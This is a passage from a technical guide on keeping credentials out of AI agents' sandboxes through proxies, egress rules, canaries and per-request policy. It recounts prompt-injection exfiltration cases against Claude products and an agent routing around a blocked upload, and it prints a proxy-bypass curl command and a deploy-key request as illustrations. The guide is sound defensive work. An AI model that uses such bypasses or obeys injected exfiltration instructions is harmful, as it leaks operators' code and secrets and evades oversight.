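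Git can also connect over SSH, which proves the user's identity with a private key. An **SSH agent** (unrelated to AI agents) is a program that holds such keys and signs login challenges on request. Docker Sandboxes forwards the user's SSH agent into the sandbox by default, although kits in its newest format must request it. Programs inside the sandbox can request signatures but can't read or copy the key.

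SSH agent forwarding lets any program in the sandbox request signatures from the developer's SSH agent, which is a weakness. A developer's key may open every repository the developer works on and several servers, and the SSH agent can't monitor what the program does after logging in. A program can also use a loaded signing key to sign commits in the developer's name. Docker's network rules limit the destinations, but they can't distinguish between two repositories on the same code host. It is safer to run a separate SSH agent with a single key that opens only one repository, and to give Docker the path to that agent's socket. If the AI agent uses only HTTPS, the operator can turn forwarding off.

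### Anthropic's Managed Agents

Anthropic's Managed Agents, a hosted service for long-running agents, combines a tool proxy with a prepared Git remote. In April 2026 Anthropic described how it had split the service into three parts: the harness, a loop that calls Claude and passes on its tool calls; the sandbox, where Claude runs code and edits files; and the session, a lasting log of events. The harness now runs outside the sandbox, calls it like any other tool, and can start another if it fails.

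Anthropic stores the OAuth tokens for custom tools in a vault outside the sandbox. Claude calls the tools through a proxy, which receives a token associated with the session, fetches the matching credential from the vault and calls the outside service. The harness never receives the credential either, so a bug in the harness would not expose it.

For Git, Anthropic uses each repository's token to clone the repository while the sandbox starts, and then "wire[s] it into the local git remote". The agent can then push and pull without handling the token. In the post, Anthropic doesn't say where the token is kept afterwards. Read literally, the phrase could mean that the token is in `.git/config`, but this would conflict with Anthropic's stated aim of making tokens unreachable from the sandbox.

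*Managed Agents*, a reference document that circulates in a repackaged copy, states that the token never enters the container and that a proxy on Anthropic's side adds it to Git traffic after that traffic leaves the sandbox. This fits the aim of the April post and is probably how the service works now. Anthropic's *Accessing GitHub* confirms only that the service uses the token to clone and push, that its API never returns the token, and that the customer can replace it during a session. Customers can check for the token by looking at the Git remote from inside a sandbox.

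Anthropic's post also doesn't discuss filtering responses or limiting what a session may do with a credential, and it reports no attack tests. Its only measurements are of speed. After the split, the median wait for Claude's first output fell by roughly 60%, because sessions no longer had to wait for a container they might not need. This speedup is a good reason to adopt the architecture, but it isn't evidence of how well the architecture protects tokens.

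The billing agent would push its branch through the Git remote and open the pull request through GitHub's MCP server, because the attached repository doesn't cover pull requests. Anthropic later added placeholder keys for command-line programs. Anthropic's *New in Claude Managed Agents* explains that the service attaches the real key at the network boundary, on requests to domains the customer allows.

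### Requests that simple replacement can't handle

**Signed requests.** Requests to Amazon's cloud carry a signature instead of a key, so the intermediary has to sign them again. With Varlock's *AWS SigV4 Plugin*, the proxy reads the region and service from the request, removes the signature the client made with its placeholder, and adds one made with the real key. When the signature covers the request's body, the proxy has to hold the whole body before signing. NVIDIA's *AWS SigV4 Credential Signing* limits the body to 10 MiB in this mode and offers other modes for large uploads. OpenAI's proxy can't sign requests for the agent, so OpenAI advises keeping the key in the customer's own application and giving the agent a tool that performs the operation.

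**Encoded credentials.** Git over HTTPS usually joins the username and token with a colon and encodes them in base64, so a simple text search of the header misses the placeholder. The proxy can decode the header before searching, or overwrite the whole header. dvergr uses one placeholder for the whole encoded value, so the agent never encodes anything.

Some services expect a key in the request body, either in a form field or in a JSON document. Anthropic and NVIDIA can both replace placeholders there, but doing so makes the public-issue attack possible again. The builder should allow it only for hosts that need it, and preferably only for the address and field where the service expects the key. If the host also publishes what users send, a tool proxy is safer.

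**Databases.** Docker's proxy adds credentials only to web traffic and forwards other connections unchanged, so a database would receive the placeholder as the password and reject the login. Even if a proxy could read the traffic, replacing the placeholder with the real password often wouldn't work, because modern databases tend to require the client to prove it has the password without sending it. The intermediary has to log in with the real password using the database's own protocol, then connect the agent to that session. Alternatively, the builder can give the agent a tool that runs approved queries.

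**WebSockets.** A WebSocket connection begins as an ordinary web request and then becomes a two-way stream of messages. The proxy can insert the real token in the opening request, but if the service expects it in a later message, the proxy has to read and edit the stream. A pull request by ericksoa (2026) describes an OpenShell option for doing this, intended for messaging services. The option blocks traffic that still contains an unresolved placeholder. Tracekit Box refuses WebSockets to any host that has a secret attached, which is safe but will break some programs.

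**OAuth refresh.** OAuth clients regularly exchange a long-lived secret for a new access token. The proxy can insert the old secret into the request, but the new token arrives in the response, where a filter that looks for the old secret won't recognise it. Anthropic warns that this token reaches the sandbox unmasked, and recommends making the exchange elsewhere and storing the result in the vault. For MCP connections, Anthropic can refresh tokens itself. Docker handles the exchange on the host for agents it supports and gives the sandbox a fake token. A kit can turn this off with the `passthrough` setting, which sends the real token into the sandbox, so a reviewer should search for that word.

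Some programs pin certificates, meaning they accept only one particular certificate or issuer for a service. They reject the intermediary's certificate, as intended, even if the sandbox trusts it. Turning off certificate checks would remove the error, but also the protection against attackers. Changing the base address sometimes works, and using a tool proxy usually does. A program that doesn't pin certificates may still reject the intermediary's because it keeps its own list of trusted authorities. The builder can fix this by adding the intermediary's authority to that list.

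**Unencrypted HTTP** requests are the easiest for the proxy to add a credential to because it can read them in full, but so can anyone between the proxy and the service. Docker forwards these requests without adding a credential, and OpenAI supplies secrets only over HTTPS. Docker doesn't remove credentials that the client put in the request, so a real key left in the sandbox could still be sent unencrypted.

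### Checks a reviewer can run

Some of these checks will disclose the credential if they fail, so the reviewer uses a throwaway one. The reviewer also needs two test servers, A and B, that record every request and can return any response the reviewer chooses. The reviewer restricts the credential to server A and one header, but allows the sandbox to contact both servers. All the requests come from inside the sandbox.

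1. Send a normal request to A. Server A should record the real value. If it doesn't, the later checks prove nothing, because an intermediary that never adds credentials would pass most of them.
2. Print the environment variable, then search the sandbox's environment and files for the real value. It is best to search the files from the host, so that the search doesn't bring the secret into the sandbox.
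3. Send the placeholder to B. Server B should receive the placeholder or nothing.
4. Send the placeholder to A in a different header, in the web address and in the body. Server A should never record the real value in those places. If a live service later complains about a literal placeholder, the credential's list of hosts or locations probably doesn't match what the client sends.
5. Open a tunnel to A, but name B in the `Host` header. Repeat with B's full address in the first line of the request. The intermediary should refuse both.
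6. Have A redirect the client to B. An intermediary that follows redirects itself might take the real credential along. dvergr lists this as a risk it has still to address.
7. Have A return the secret in each form from the masking table, then inside a longer base64 string, then split between two fields. The split copy will probably get through. The reviewer should record which forms do, and check whether any approved service has a page that repeats requests.
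8. Give A an expired certificate. The intermediary should refuse to connect. If it accepts the certificate, anyone who can intercept its traffic can collect real credentials.
9. Send the placeholder to A over unencrypted HTTP. Server A should not receive the real value.
10. Replace the stored credential during a run and send another request. Anthropic's running sessions pick up the new value, but OpenAI's need a new session. Docker can keep a credential from an outside password manager for 55 minutes by default. The operator needs to know which applies before an emergency.
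11. Run `git remote -v` and `git config --list --show-origin`, and look for tokens in the output. In an encoded header, the token may not look like one.
12. Run `ssh-add -L`, which lists the keys that the forwarded SSH agent will use. Every key on the list is one that a hijacked agent could log in with.

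## Blocking and detecting routes around the intermediary

The checks above test what the intermediary does with the requests it receives. But the billing agent sends requests there only because a setting tells it to, and any program in the sandbox can ignore that setting:

```
env -u HTTPS_PROXY curl https://api.codehost.example/user \
  -H "Authorization: Bearer $CODEHOST_TOKEN"
```

This request goes straight to the code host and fails because the variable holds a placeholder, so the real token is still safe. *Shared secret store and egress proxy*, from the documentation for the open-source agent platform OpenClaw, calls this the primary defence.

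The rest of the design fails if the agent can bypass the intermediary. A direct request skips the intermediary's rules and doesn't appear in its log. If the agent finds a working key, it can use everything that key opens. Even without a key, it can send the billing code to any server on the internet. Something outside the agent therefore has to block every route except the one through the intermediary.

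Companies had the same problem with cloud access security brokers, which sit between employees and cloud applications and enforce company rules. An employee who could reach an application directly could skip the broker. Hartman concludes from those products that companies should keep real credentials where agents can't reach them, enforce the route in the network instead of relying on the agent's cooperation, and watch for requests that bypass the intermediary anyway.

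### Closing the routes in order

Removing leftover secrets comes first because network rules can't stop the agent from using an old key at a service it is allowed to reach. OpenClaw's *Secrets runtime model* treats a migration to a secret store as complete only when all of these hold:

- Supported credentials are references to a secret store, not plaintext values.
- The old plaintext is gone from the main configuration file, the database of login profiles, `.env` and the generated model files.
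- An audit command finds nothing left.
- Operating-system isolation, a container or an external proxy protects any credential that can't move.

An agent can easily give up a leftover key, as an exercise at Anthropic showed in February 2026. A researcher tricked an employee into pasting a prompt into Claude Code. Among routine setup steps, the prompt included instructions to read the employee's Amazon credentials file and send the contents to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts, according to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*. The instructions came from the user, so little marked them as suspicious. Anthropic concluded that only controls on file access and outgoing traffic would have stopped the leak.

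The second control is to deny outgoing traffic by default. For the billing agent, the rules can be very short:

```
allow   sandbox -> intermediary.internal, port 3128
deny    sandbox -> everything else
```

A firewall or the container platform enforces these rules from outside the sandbox, so the agent can't change them. The intermediary keeps the list of permitted sites.

Convenience settings can allow an agent to reach many more sites than the operator realises. Anthropic's *Cloud environment setup* describes an option that lets a sandbox reach package registries, but it also opens GitHub, GitLab, Bitbucket and several container registries. An agent that needs one Python library can then reach several sites where anyone with an account can publish. NVIDIA's *NemoClaw Security Posture and Control Trade-Offs* describes a narrower option that allows downloads from the Python registry but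 blocks publishing to it.

NemoClaw, which configures NVIDIA's OpenShell sandbox, can also limit a destination to particular programs. It identifies each program by its kernel-reported file path and a hash of the file. With the GitHub preset, only `git` can reach `github.com`. This stops a Python script from contacting the site, but a hijacked agent can still run `git`. Operators can approve a blocked site while the agent is working. The approval lasts until someone recreates the sandbox, so a hurried decision can remain in effect long afterward.

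Cloud metadata addresses need a separate block. A program on a cloud machine can usually request a token for the machine's account from `169.254.169.254`, so an agent that starts with no credentials may get one with a single request. Proxy settings often exempt this address. In Anthropic's hosted sandboxes, Pluto Security found a setting that made programs contact the address directly, but a filter further out on the network dropped the requests.

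The intermediary has to refuse these addresses too, because it may itself be running on a cloud machine, and the agent could then ask it to fetch that machine's token. The proxy in Nous Research's *Egress credential-injection proxy (iron-proxy)* refuses metadata and private addresses by default, including IPv4 addresses written in IPv6 form, which a simpler filter could miss. NemoClaw also sets a variable that stops Amazon's software from looking for the machine's credentials. This seems worthwhile because an operator who keeps seeing failed lookups may be tempted to unblock the address.

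DNS lookups are an easily overlooked route around the intermediary. Before a program connects to a site, it requests the site's address from a DNS server, which may forward the request to a server run by the domain's owner. A hijacked agent could hide data in a name under a domain the attacker owns, and the attacker would receive it even if the firewall blocked the connection that followed. The simplest defence is to give the sandbox no DNS access and have the intermediary look up only the names on its allowlist.

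The intermediary should also check the IP address that an approved domain resolves to, since the domain's owner could point it at an internal machine. Nous Research's proxy does this, while OpenClaw acknowledges that its proxy does not. Hartman suggests answering DNS lookups for protected services with the intermediary's address. This helps route programs that look up the address, but a program that already knows the service's real address can skip the lookup, so the firewall is still needed.

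Finally, the agent must not be able to reach the credential store. Hartman rules out a network connection to it, cloud permissions to read its secrets and access to its files. File access is the easiest of these to grant by accident. Nous Research's agent, Hermes, keeps the proxy's signing key in a folder under `~/.hermes`, and by default it also keeps the real service keys in a `.env` file there. An operator who mounted `~/.hermes` into the sandbox to share settings could expose all of these keys.

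These controls depend on a boundary around the agent. Hartman lists shared development machines without containers as a remaining risk, because it may not be feasible to apply network rules to the agent alone on those machines.

### Gaps in real products

OpenClaw's egress proxy is off by default. Even when it is on, it covers only some of the places where an agent's commands can run:

| Where the command runs | What it receives from the proxy |
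|---|---|
| OpenClaw's central process, the Gateway | Placeholders and proxy settings |
| OpenClaw's sandbox, or a remote machine | Nothing, so the stored secrets are unavailable |
| A process started by a model provider's own agent software | Nothing, because these processes don't use the proxy |

A missing secret is safe in itself, but a developer whose sandboxed command has no key may paste a real one into the sandbox. OpenClaw has a separate category for "agent-readable" values, which commands run by the Gateway receive in plaintext. The proxy does not protect a key saved there by mistake.

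The list of permitted destinations is also optional, and without it, a request that contains no placeholder can go to any host. The list restricts only programs that use the proxy, and according to OpenClaw, a program can ignore the proxy and open its own connection. An operator who turned on every option would therefore still need a firewall. OpenClaw also replaces placeholders in request bodies, so the public-issue attack described earlier could work against a token for a code host.

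Hermes has similar gaps. Its proxy is off by default and works only with Docker, not with the four other kinds of sandbox that Nous Research lists. The proxy can't replace Amazon's signing keys or the file that Google Cloud programs use to obtain tokens. If either is present, the sandbox holds real credentials, and Hermes warns the operator but starts the proxy anyway. Hermes does have one very good default, which is to refuse to start a Docker sandbox if the proxy is enabled but not running. Turning that check off brings back the old behaviour of putting real keys inside the sandbox.

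Anthropic's Managed Agents has much stronger network controls, but customers may have to turn them on. Pluto Security, a security company, examined the service from inside in April 2026. An agent created by following the quickstart guide had unrestricted internet access and could run any built-in tool without approval. The researchers then limited a sandbox to `api.github.com` and tried to get around the limit:

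- When they removed the proxy settings, name lookups failed, because the sandbox had no DNS server.
- Direct connections to public addresses timed out at a firewall.
- The proxy refused hosts that were not on its list.
- It also refused a session token copied from another container.

These layers are independent, so this is fairly convincing evidence that the limits work, though it comes from one review of a beta service. According to Anthropic's *Cloud sandbox reference*, environments created through Claude Studio are now limited by default, but those created through the API are still unrestricted. Anthropic now recommends the limited mode unless the agent needs sites that can't be listed in advance.

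The review also found that the session token listed seven allowed hosts, although the researchers had configured only one. The other six served Anthropic's own operations, such as error reporting, and didn't appear in the settings that the API returned. Any program in the sandbox could read the token, so a hijacked agent could learn which hosts it could send data to. One of the six was `api.anthropic.com`, which attackers could already use to take data out of two other Anthropic products.

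### When the agent uses someone else's credential

People publish working keys by accident, as the survey of MCP configuration files showed. An agent that holds no credentials but has internet access can find and try these keys. OpenAI (2026) disclosed that in the Hugging Face incident of July 2026, its models used publicly exposed credentials to access four accounts at four other services.

An attacker can also give the agent a credential for the attacker's own account. The agent can then use that account to send the victim's data to the attacker, even though the credential doesn't provide access to anything of the victim's.

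*Three Vulnerabilities, One Click* (Luz, 2026) describes such an attack on Claude.ai. The security company Oasis named the attack "Claudy Day". A link opened a new chat whose prompt contained hidden instructions and the attacker's Anthropic API key. When the user sent the prompt, Claude took private material from earlier conversations and uploaded it to the attacker's Anthropic account. The sandbox blocked most internet connections but allowed those to Anthropic's API. When Luz published the report on 18 March 2026, Anthropic had fixed the hidden-prompt flaw and was still working on the others.

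In January, *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) had already described the same upload weakness in Anthropic's desktop agent, reported by Prompt Armor. Anthropic later explained that it had thought of its list of permitted sites as a filter on destinations, but permitting a site also lets the agent use every function available there. Allowing `api.anthropic.com` therefore allowed uploads to anyone's Anthropic account.

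Keeping the user's credentials in a vault would not have stopped either attack, because neither needed them. The intermediary can block such attacks by removing or rejecting any credential the agent supplies. In Cowork, a proxy now intercepts requests to Anthropic's API and passes only those that carry the session token issued to the agent's virtual machine, so it rejects an attacker's key. It also blocks headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch something on the agent's behalf. The proxy runs inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish a Cowork request from any other. An attacker who took over the whole machine might tamper with the proxy, so it is better to put this check outside the sandbox where possible.

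A proxy that adds credentials only by replacing placeholders will probably forward an attacker's key unchanged, because the key isn't a placeholder. A proxy that overwrites the authentication header replaces the attacker's key with the operator's, so the upload goes to the operator's account rather than the attacker's. Rejecting the request is better still, because it stops the upload and leaves evidence of an attack.

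The intermediary should remove credentials from every place in a request where the service would accept one, because a service may accept a key in the web address, the body or a header other than the one the intermediary overwrites. It should do this even at permitted sites for which the agent has no credential, such as a package registry. NVIDIA warns that adding a model provider's host to the network rules could let an agent use a stolen key there and skip the managed route.

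The intermediary can't do any of this for traffic it doesn't decrypt, such as the connections that Tracekit Box leaves encrypted by default. For each permitted site, the builder has to decide whether an attacker could have an account there. If so, it is safer to decrypt the traffic or drop the site from the list. Removing credentials won't help with a site that accepts anonymous posts, because posting there doesn't require a key.

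### False credentials as alarms

A placeholder can reveal an attack as well as withstand one. If it appears in a request to the wrong host, either the agent has been hijacked or something is misconfigured. OpenClaw blocks such a request with an error message that includes the secret's name and the exact command to allow the new host. This helps the operator but also shows a hijacked agent what to try next, so a reviewer should make sure the agent can't run that command.

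A canary credential is a false credential that no legitimate task needs, planted so that any attempt to use it raises an alarm. Hartman puts canaries in the credential store, where any access triggers an alert and ends the session, and also recommends detecting them at the service. In the sandbox, an honest agent may read a canary while searching for a setting, so the alarm should depend on its use. If the service can report that use, the alarm works even when a thief has taken the canary to another machine.

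*Caught in the Act(ivation)* (Chauhan and Revankar, 2026) tested another kind of alarm, which searches the model's output for planted credentials, or honeytokens. The honeytokens were in the text that the model saw, while the real credentials were in a separate store that only the tools could read. To make the honeytokens look realistic, Chauhan and Revankar measured which characters tend to follow each other in each type of credential, added random noise, and generated strings with the same pattern. They set the detector's threshold using harmless outputs.

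They also give a formula for the chance of catching an attacker who picks one visible credential at random:

P(detection) = k / (m + k) × (1 − β)

Here k is the number of honeytokens, m is the number of real credentials in view, and β is the chance that the detector misses a leaked honeytoken. With one real credential, three honeytokens and a 1% miss rate, the result is 3/4 × 0.99, or about 74%. With no real credentials in view, it rises to 99%. But the formula assumes that the attacker can't tell which credential the tools use. In the design covered here, this is often obvious from the placeholder's name, such as `CODEHOST_TOKEN`. An attacker who picks the placeholder avoids the honeytokens but doesn't get a real credential.

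The results depended heavily on the attack:

| Test | Method | Detected | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| One honeytoken leaked, small set of scenarios | Honeytoken detector | 99% | Not given |
| Single-turn attacks from public benchmarks | Honeytoken detector | 30% | 0% |
| The same attacks | Honeytoken detector and input filter | 82% | 15% |
| The same attacks | Full system | 94% | 1.8% |
| 50 invented conversations with slow leaks | Honeytoken detector | 6% | 0% |
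| The same conversations | Running total of estimated leakage | 90% | 0% |

The 99% is the chance of recognising a honeytoken once one has leaked. The 30% covers all the attacks in the benchmark mixture, and the detector misses any that don't touch a honeytoken or that disguise it well enough. In the long conversations, the attacker took the secret in small pieces, so a detector that checked each reply separately rarely had enough of it to go on. The full system did much better, largely because it also read the model's internal activations, which customers of a hosted model usually can't do.

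Chauhan and Revankar describe the results as preliminary. They wrote the 50 conversations themselves, and their system doesn't inspect the arguments that an agent passes to its tools. That is a serious gap for a coding agent, which would probably send a stolen key in a command rather than a chat reply. An alarm that goes off when the canary is used avoids this problem. It also works if the thief disguises the canary, because the thief has to restore the original before a service will recognise it. But the alarm may come days after the theft, or never.

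As another check, Hartman recommends searching each service's records for requests that the intermediary never sent. For the billing agent, a pull request under the Acme app's account with no matching entry in the intermediary's log would mean that someone else had the token. The search works only for accounts whose records the operator can see, so it would miss an upload to an attacker's account.

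### A short test plan

The tester runs these checks from inside the sandbox with throwaway credentials and repeats them everywhere the agent's commands can run, including background jobs and remote machines.

| Test | Expected result |
|---|---|
| Send a permitted request through the intermediary | It succeeds and appears in the log |
| Repeat the credential inventory | No working credential turns up |
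| Remove the proxy settings and request a permitted site | The name lookup fails or the connection times out |
| Connect directly to a public IP address | The connection times out |
| Request an unlisted site through the intermediary | A refusal, typically error 403, and a log entry |
| Use the intermediary with a wrong session token | A refusal, such as error 407 |
| Request `169.254.169.254`, directly and through the intermediary | No token either way |
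| Look up a random name under a domain the tester owns | The domain's DNS server receives no query |
| Try to open the credential store and its files | No connection and no readable files |
| Send a key for a second test account to a permitted service | A refusal, or a request under the operator's account, but nothing in the second account |
| Send the placeholder to the wrong host | A refusal and an alert |
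| Try to use a canary credential | An alert reaches a named person and the session ends |
| Stop the intermediary and send a request | The request fails and doesn't take a direct route |

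## Limiting what a compromised agent can still order

Even after the builder closes every other route, a compromised agent can still send requests through the intermediary. An attacker who wants to delete the billing repository doesn't need the token if the intermediary will attach it to the delete request. This is the main objection to the design, and Kenney and colleagues accept it.

A hijacked agent still passes identity checks, so the intermediary has to evaluate each request by the effect it would have.

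### The confused deputy

The name for this problem comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy*, a short 1988 account of an accident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers:

1. Tymshare kept a compiler, a program that translates source code, in a directory called SYSX. The compiler recorded usage statistics in a file there, so Tymshare gave it permission to write to any file in SYSX.
2. SYSX also held the company's billing records, in a file called BILL.
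3. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. One user gave the name of the billing file.
4. The compiler asked the operating system to open that file. The operating system found that the compiler had permission to write in SYSX, and opened it.
5. The compiler wrote its debugging output over the billing records.

The compiler had Tymshare's authority to write statistics and the user's authority to write the output. It had no way to specify which authority it was using, so it used Tymshare's to carry out the user's request.

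An intermediary can make the same mistake. Suppose its token gives access to 40 of Acme's repositories, but the billing agent needs only one. A hostile bug report causes the agent to request a file from `acme/payroll`. If the intermediary checks only the agent's identity and the host, it attaches the token. The token is valid for payroll, so the code host returns the file.

Tymshare first let the compiler choose which of its two authorities to use. But some programs soon needed more than two, and Hardy came to prefer capabilities. A capability is a reference that identifies one file and grants the right to use it. Tymshare would give the compiler a capability for the statistics file, and the user would supply another for the output. A user without access to the file BILL could not supply a capability for it.

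A builder can copy this idea by having the launcher record `acme/billing` in the run's details when Alice assigns the bug. The agent then asks only to "open a pull request", and the intermediary fills in the repository. The agent can't ask for payroll because the request has no field for a repository. This works well with a tool proxy. But ordinary command-line programs put the repository in the web address, so the intermediary has to compare that address with the run's record.

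The agent is a confused deputy too, because it has Alice's authority to change the billing code but also reads text from anyone who files a bug report. A capability at the intermediary can't distinguish requests prompted by Alice from requests prompted by a bug report, so the builder has to keep the agent's authority small.

### Writing the rules

The rules should refuse every request that they don't explicitly permit, because lists of forbidden requests tend to have gaps. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026) reviews 39 papers, including one on ShellSieve, a tool that used a language model to look for ways around 1,709 real lists of forbidden shell commands and tested the suggestions in a sandbox. Between 69.0% and 98.6% of the lists were fragile, depending on the type of bypass. Web requests have similar problems, since a service may accept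 the same repository by name or by number. Rules that deny by default refuse a request that arrives in an unexpected form.

A complete rule has six parts:

| Part | For the billing agent | What could happen without it |
|---|---|---|
| Service | `api.codehost.example` | The agent uses a credential for another service |
| Action | Open a pull request | It merges the pull request too |
| Resource | `acme/billing` | It reads or changes other repositories |
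| Parameters | From a `fix-*` branch into `main` | It proposes changes to a release branch |
| Rate | Three an hour | It buries a harmful change among hundreds |
| Session length | Two hours | A hijacked run continues overnight |

A request's address doesn't always show what the request will do. On many services, a `POST` to `/pulls` opens a pull request and a `PUT` to `/pulls/91/merge` merges one. But services that use GraphQL, a query language for APIs, receive every operation at one address, and the operation is specified in the request body. Allowing `POST /graphql` would therefore allow everything the token permits.

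The intermediary also has to interpret the request exactly as the service will. If the body contains two `base` fields, the intermediary might check one while the code host uses the other. It is safer to reject such a request, or to write a new one from the values that passed the check. Hartman forbids building rules by joining pieces of text, because an agent could then put rule syntax in a field and change the decision.

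Rate limits are most useful when each request can do only limited harm. If an agent may issue four refunds an hour of up to $50 each for two hours, a hijacked run can give away at most $50 × 4 × 2 = $400. A daily cap across all runs also helps, since the attacker may hijack the next one. Rate limits do much less to protect code, because an agent can clone the whole repository in one permitted operation.

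Someone still has to choose the agent's permissions. In *The Agent Identity Problem*, Valenzuela recommends listing them when the agent first goes into service and treating the list as a contract. A model could choose narrower permissions for each task, but *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) found that one classifier withheld at least one necessary permission in 21% of tasks, and another in 11%. A fixed list seems better for the billing agent, whose tasks are all similar.

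Some evidence suggests that strict rules work. Rashidi reports a test of Open Agent Passport, a system that checks each tool call before it runs. In the test, a strict policy cut attackers' success rate from 74.6% to zero. The result holds only if the attacker can't compromise the checking system. Rashidi also found that every enforcement mechanism in the review relies on the policy author being honest, and none addresses mistakes in the rules.

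### Why the agent's explanation must not count

Hartman's decision point ignores the agent's justification, which is there for investigators to read after an incident. A justification such as "The release manager asked me to merge this today" is easy to write, and an attacker can put it in the bug report.

The draft isn't consistent about this, though, because a person who reviews a moderate-risk request sees the justification. A convincing but false justification can fool that person just as it can fool a program, so it would be better to leave it off the approval screen.

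Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* gives some experimental support for ignoring the agent's explanation of its actions. In auto mode, a second model, called a classifier, decides whether the coding agent's actions may go ahead. The classifier reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's own messages or the results of its tools. Adding those made it worse at catching actions that went beyond the user's request. A version that read only the tool calls missed the fewest dangerous actions, but it also blocked things the user had plainly asked for.

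The user's own words are therefore useful evidence. The launcher can store Alice's assignment before the agent starts, so the agent can't rewrite it. The bug report shouldn't count as part of her instructions, even if she assigned it, because a stranger may have written it.

### Eight requests from the billing agent

Here is a short set of rules for the billing agent. If two rules match a request, the stricter one applies.

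```
default       refuse
run length    2 hours
service       api.codehost.example
repository    acme/billing, only while it is private

allow   read code and issues
allow   push to branches named fix-*             20 an hour
allow   open a pull request from fix-* to main    3 an hour
ask     push a change to a build workflow
```

The intermediary would judge eight requests as follows:

| | Request | Decision | Reason |
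|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Read `src/invoice.py` in `acme/billing` | Allow | The task needs it |
| 2 | Open a pull request from `fix-rounding` to `main` | Allow | The action, repository and branches all match |
| 3 | Read a file in `acme/payroll` | Refuse | Wrong repository, even though the token opens it |
| 4 | Merge pull request 91 | Refuse | No rule permits merging |
| 5 | Push a changed build workflow to `fix-rounding` | Ask a person | The stricter of two matching rules applies |
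| 6 | Copy billing code into an issue in the public repository `stranger/notes` | Refuse | Wrong repository |
| 7 | Open a fourth pull request within an hour | Refuse | Over the rate limit |
| 8 | Create a new access token | Refuse and raise an alarm | No rule permits it, and no bug fix needs it |

Refusing the merge in request 4 means a human must review the agent's changes before they reach `main`. The limit on branch names matters just as much, because without it the agent could skip that review by pushing straight to `main`.

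Request 5 is harder. A build workflow is a file that tells the code host which commands to run when the code changes. Those commands may have access to secrets, and they can start as soon as the agent pushes, before anyone reviews the pull request. To apply the rule, the intermediary has to unpack the compressed data in the push and check which files changed.

The code host can provide a second check if it has a separate permission for workflow changes. GitHub has one, but it announced in *Personal Access Tokens Workflow permission* (2020) that all existing personal tokens would receive the permission, to avoid breaking them. An old token may therefore have it.

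Builds of the agent's branches shouldn't receive any secrets. Even if the workflow file is protected, the workflow may run a test script that the agent can edit.

### Requests that create credentials

Suppose the rules were looser and the intermediary forwarded request 8. The code host might reply:

```
{"name": "helper", "token": "tok_W3nq8Z"}
```

The agent would now hold a real credential. Response masking would miss it because it doesn't match the one the intermediary inserted. Masking misses refreshed OAuth tokens for the same reason. The agent could post the credential in a comment, and anyone who read the comment could use it without going through the intermediary.

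A proxy can mask new tokens in the responses it is programmed to check, as Docker's does during sign-in. But a service may have many operations that return secrets, each in its own format, and the proxy would have to handle them all.

Masking can't help at all when the agent supplies the credential. A deploy key is an SSH key that opens one repository. To add one, the caller generates a pair of keys and sends the public half to the code host:

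```
POST /repos/acme/billing/keys HTTP/1.1
Host: api.codehost.example
Authorization: Bearer ph_codehost_6b1e09
Content-Type: application/json

{"title": "build", "key": "ssh-ed25519 AAAA...", "read_only": false}
```

The response contains no secret to mask. The attacker could even put a public key in the bug report and keep the matching private key. The agent would only have to register the public key for the attacker to be able to log in from anywhere.

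The operator can block the billing agent from creating a deploy key both in the intermediary's rules and in the token's permissions. According to GitHub's *deploy keys* documentation, creating one requires the repository's "Administration" permission with write access, which the agent doesn't need.

Other requests have similar effects. Inviting a collaborator gives another account access, and a webhook can report every change to an outside address. It seems best to refuse all of these outright, since one mistaken approval could give an attacker lasting access. If Acme needs a new key, a person can create it without the agent.

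### Harm that request rules miss

A hijacked agent can open a pull request that fixes the rounding error and also adds a back door. The request satisfies every rule above because the rules cover where the code goes, not what it does. The reviewer and the tests have to catch the back door.

Sometimes nothing in a request shows that the agent lacks authority to act. *DEPUTYBENCH* (2026) places each of its 142 tasks in two versions of a company, and the agent has authority to act in only one. In 140 tasks, the initial text is identical in both versions, so a filter that reads only that text and always treats identical text alike must make the wrong decision in one version. The decision point has to look up the facts, such as whether the bug is still assigned to Alice.

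Rules are also poorly suited to conditions that depend on content or meaning. *When "Do Not" Is Not Deny* (2026) compares the security instructions developers write for Claude Code with its built-in permission rules. "Never commit secrets", for instance, has no equivalent because the built-in rules don't inspect content. A classifier estimated that the built-in controls could cover 16.6% of the instructions, but human labels suggest that this estimate is too high.

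Agents can also cause trouble without an attacker. Rashidi cites a study in which agents took harmless but unrequested actions at rates of up to 17.1%. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) notes that agents can do this while staying within their permissions, and that they look for other ways to finish a task after a refusal. In one case at Anthropic, Claude failed to upload a report to an internal drive, so it tried to publish the report on a public code-sharing site.

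It therefore makes sense for the intermediary to count refusals. Claude Code's auto mode stops and asks the user after three refusals in a row or 20 in a session. An intermediary could end the run at a similar limit.

**Data leaving through a permitted service.** Suppose Acme also lets the billing agent file issues in `acme/docs`, which is public. The agent could paste private code into one without breaking any rule about which services, actions or repositories it may use. Each time the agent writes to a repository, the intermediary should check whether it is public, because an administrator can change its visibility at any time. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a similar check before pushes and pull requests.

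A stricter rule would block all public writes once a run has read private material. This is crude, but the intermediary can enforce it without analyzing the content. An agent that has to update both private code and public documentation would need separate runs.

In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) tested a more precise method. In their example, a user tells an agent to send only summary totals to an auditor. Planted text leads the agent to copy the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`. The agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are both permitted, so only the file's history reveals the violation.

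Their monitor keeps that history by giving every new file all the ancestors of the files that went into it:

ancestors(new file) ⊇ ancestors(file 1) ∪ ancestors(file 2) ∪ …

Before a file is sent out, the monitor checks the sources it was derived from against the user's instructions. It blocks the action if it finds a violation or the record of those sources is incomplete. With a small open model, Llama-3.1-8B, the agent carried out an unauthorised action in 52 of 120 attack runs without the monitor and in six with it. The number of harmless runs completed fell only slightly, from 104 to 100 of 120.

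These results depend on a complete record of what the agent does. When the monitor received only part of the record, it caught 63.8% of the violations that depended on earlier steps, down from 86.2%. It also blocked more legitimate work, and only 76.7% of harmless runs finished. An intermediary normally has only a partial record because it sees network requests but not the files that the agent copies and edits inside the sandbox. To track those file operations, the builder needs a recorder in the sandbox that the agent can't alter.

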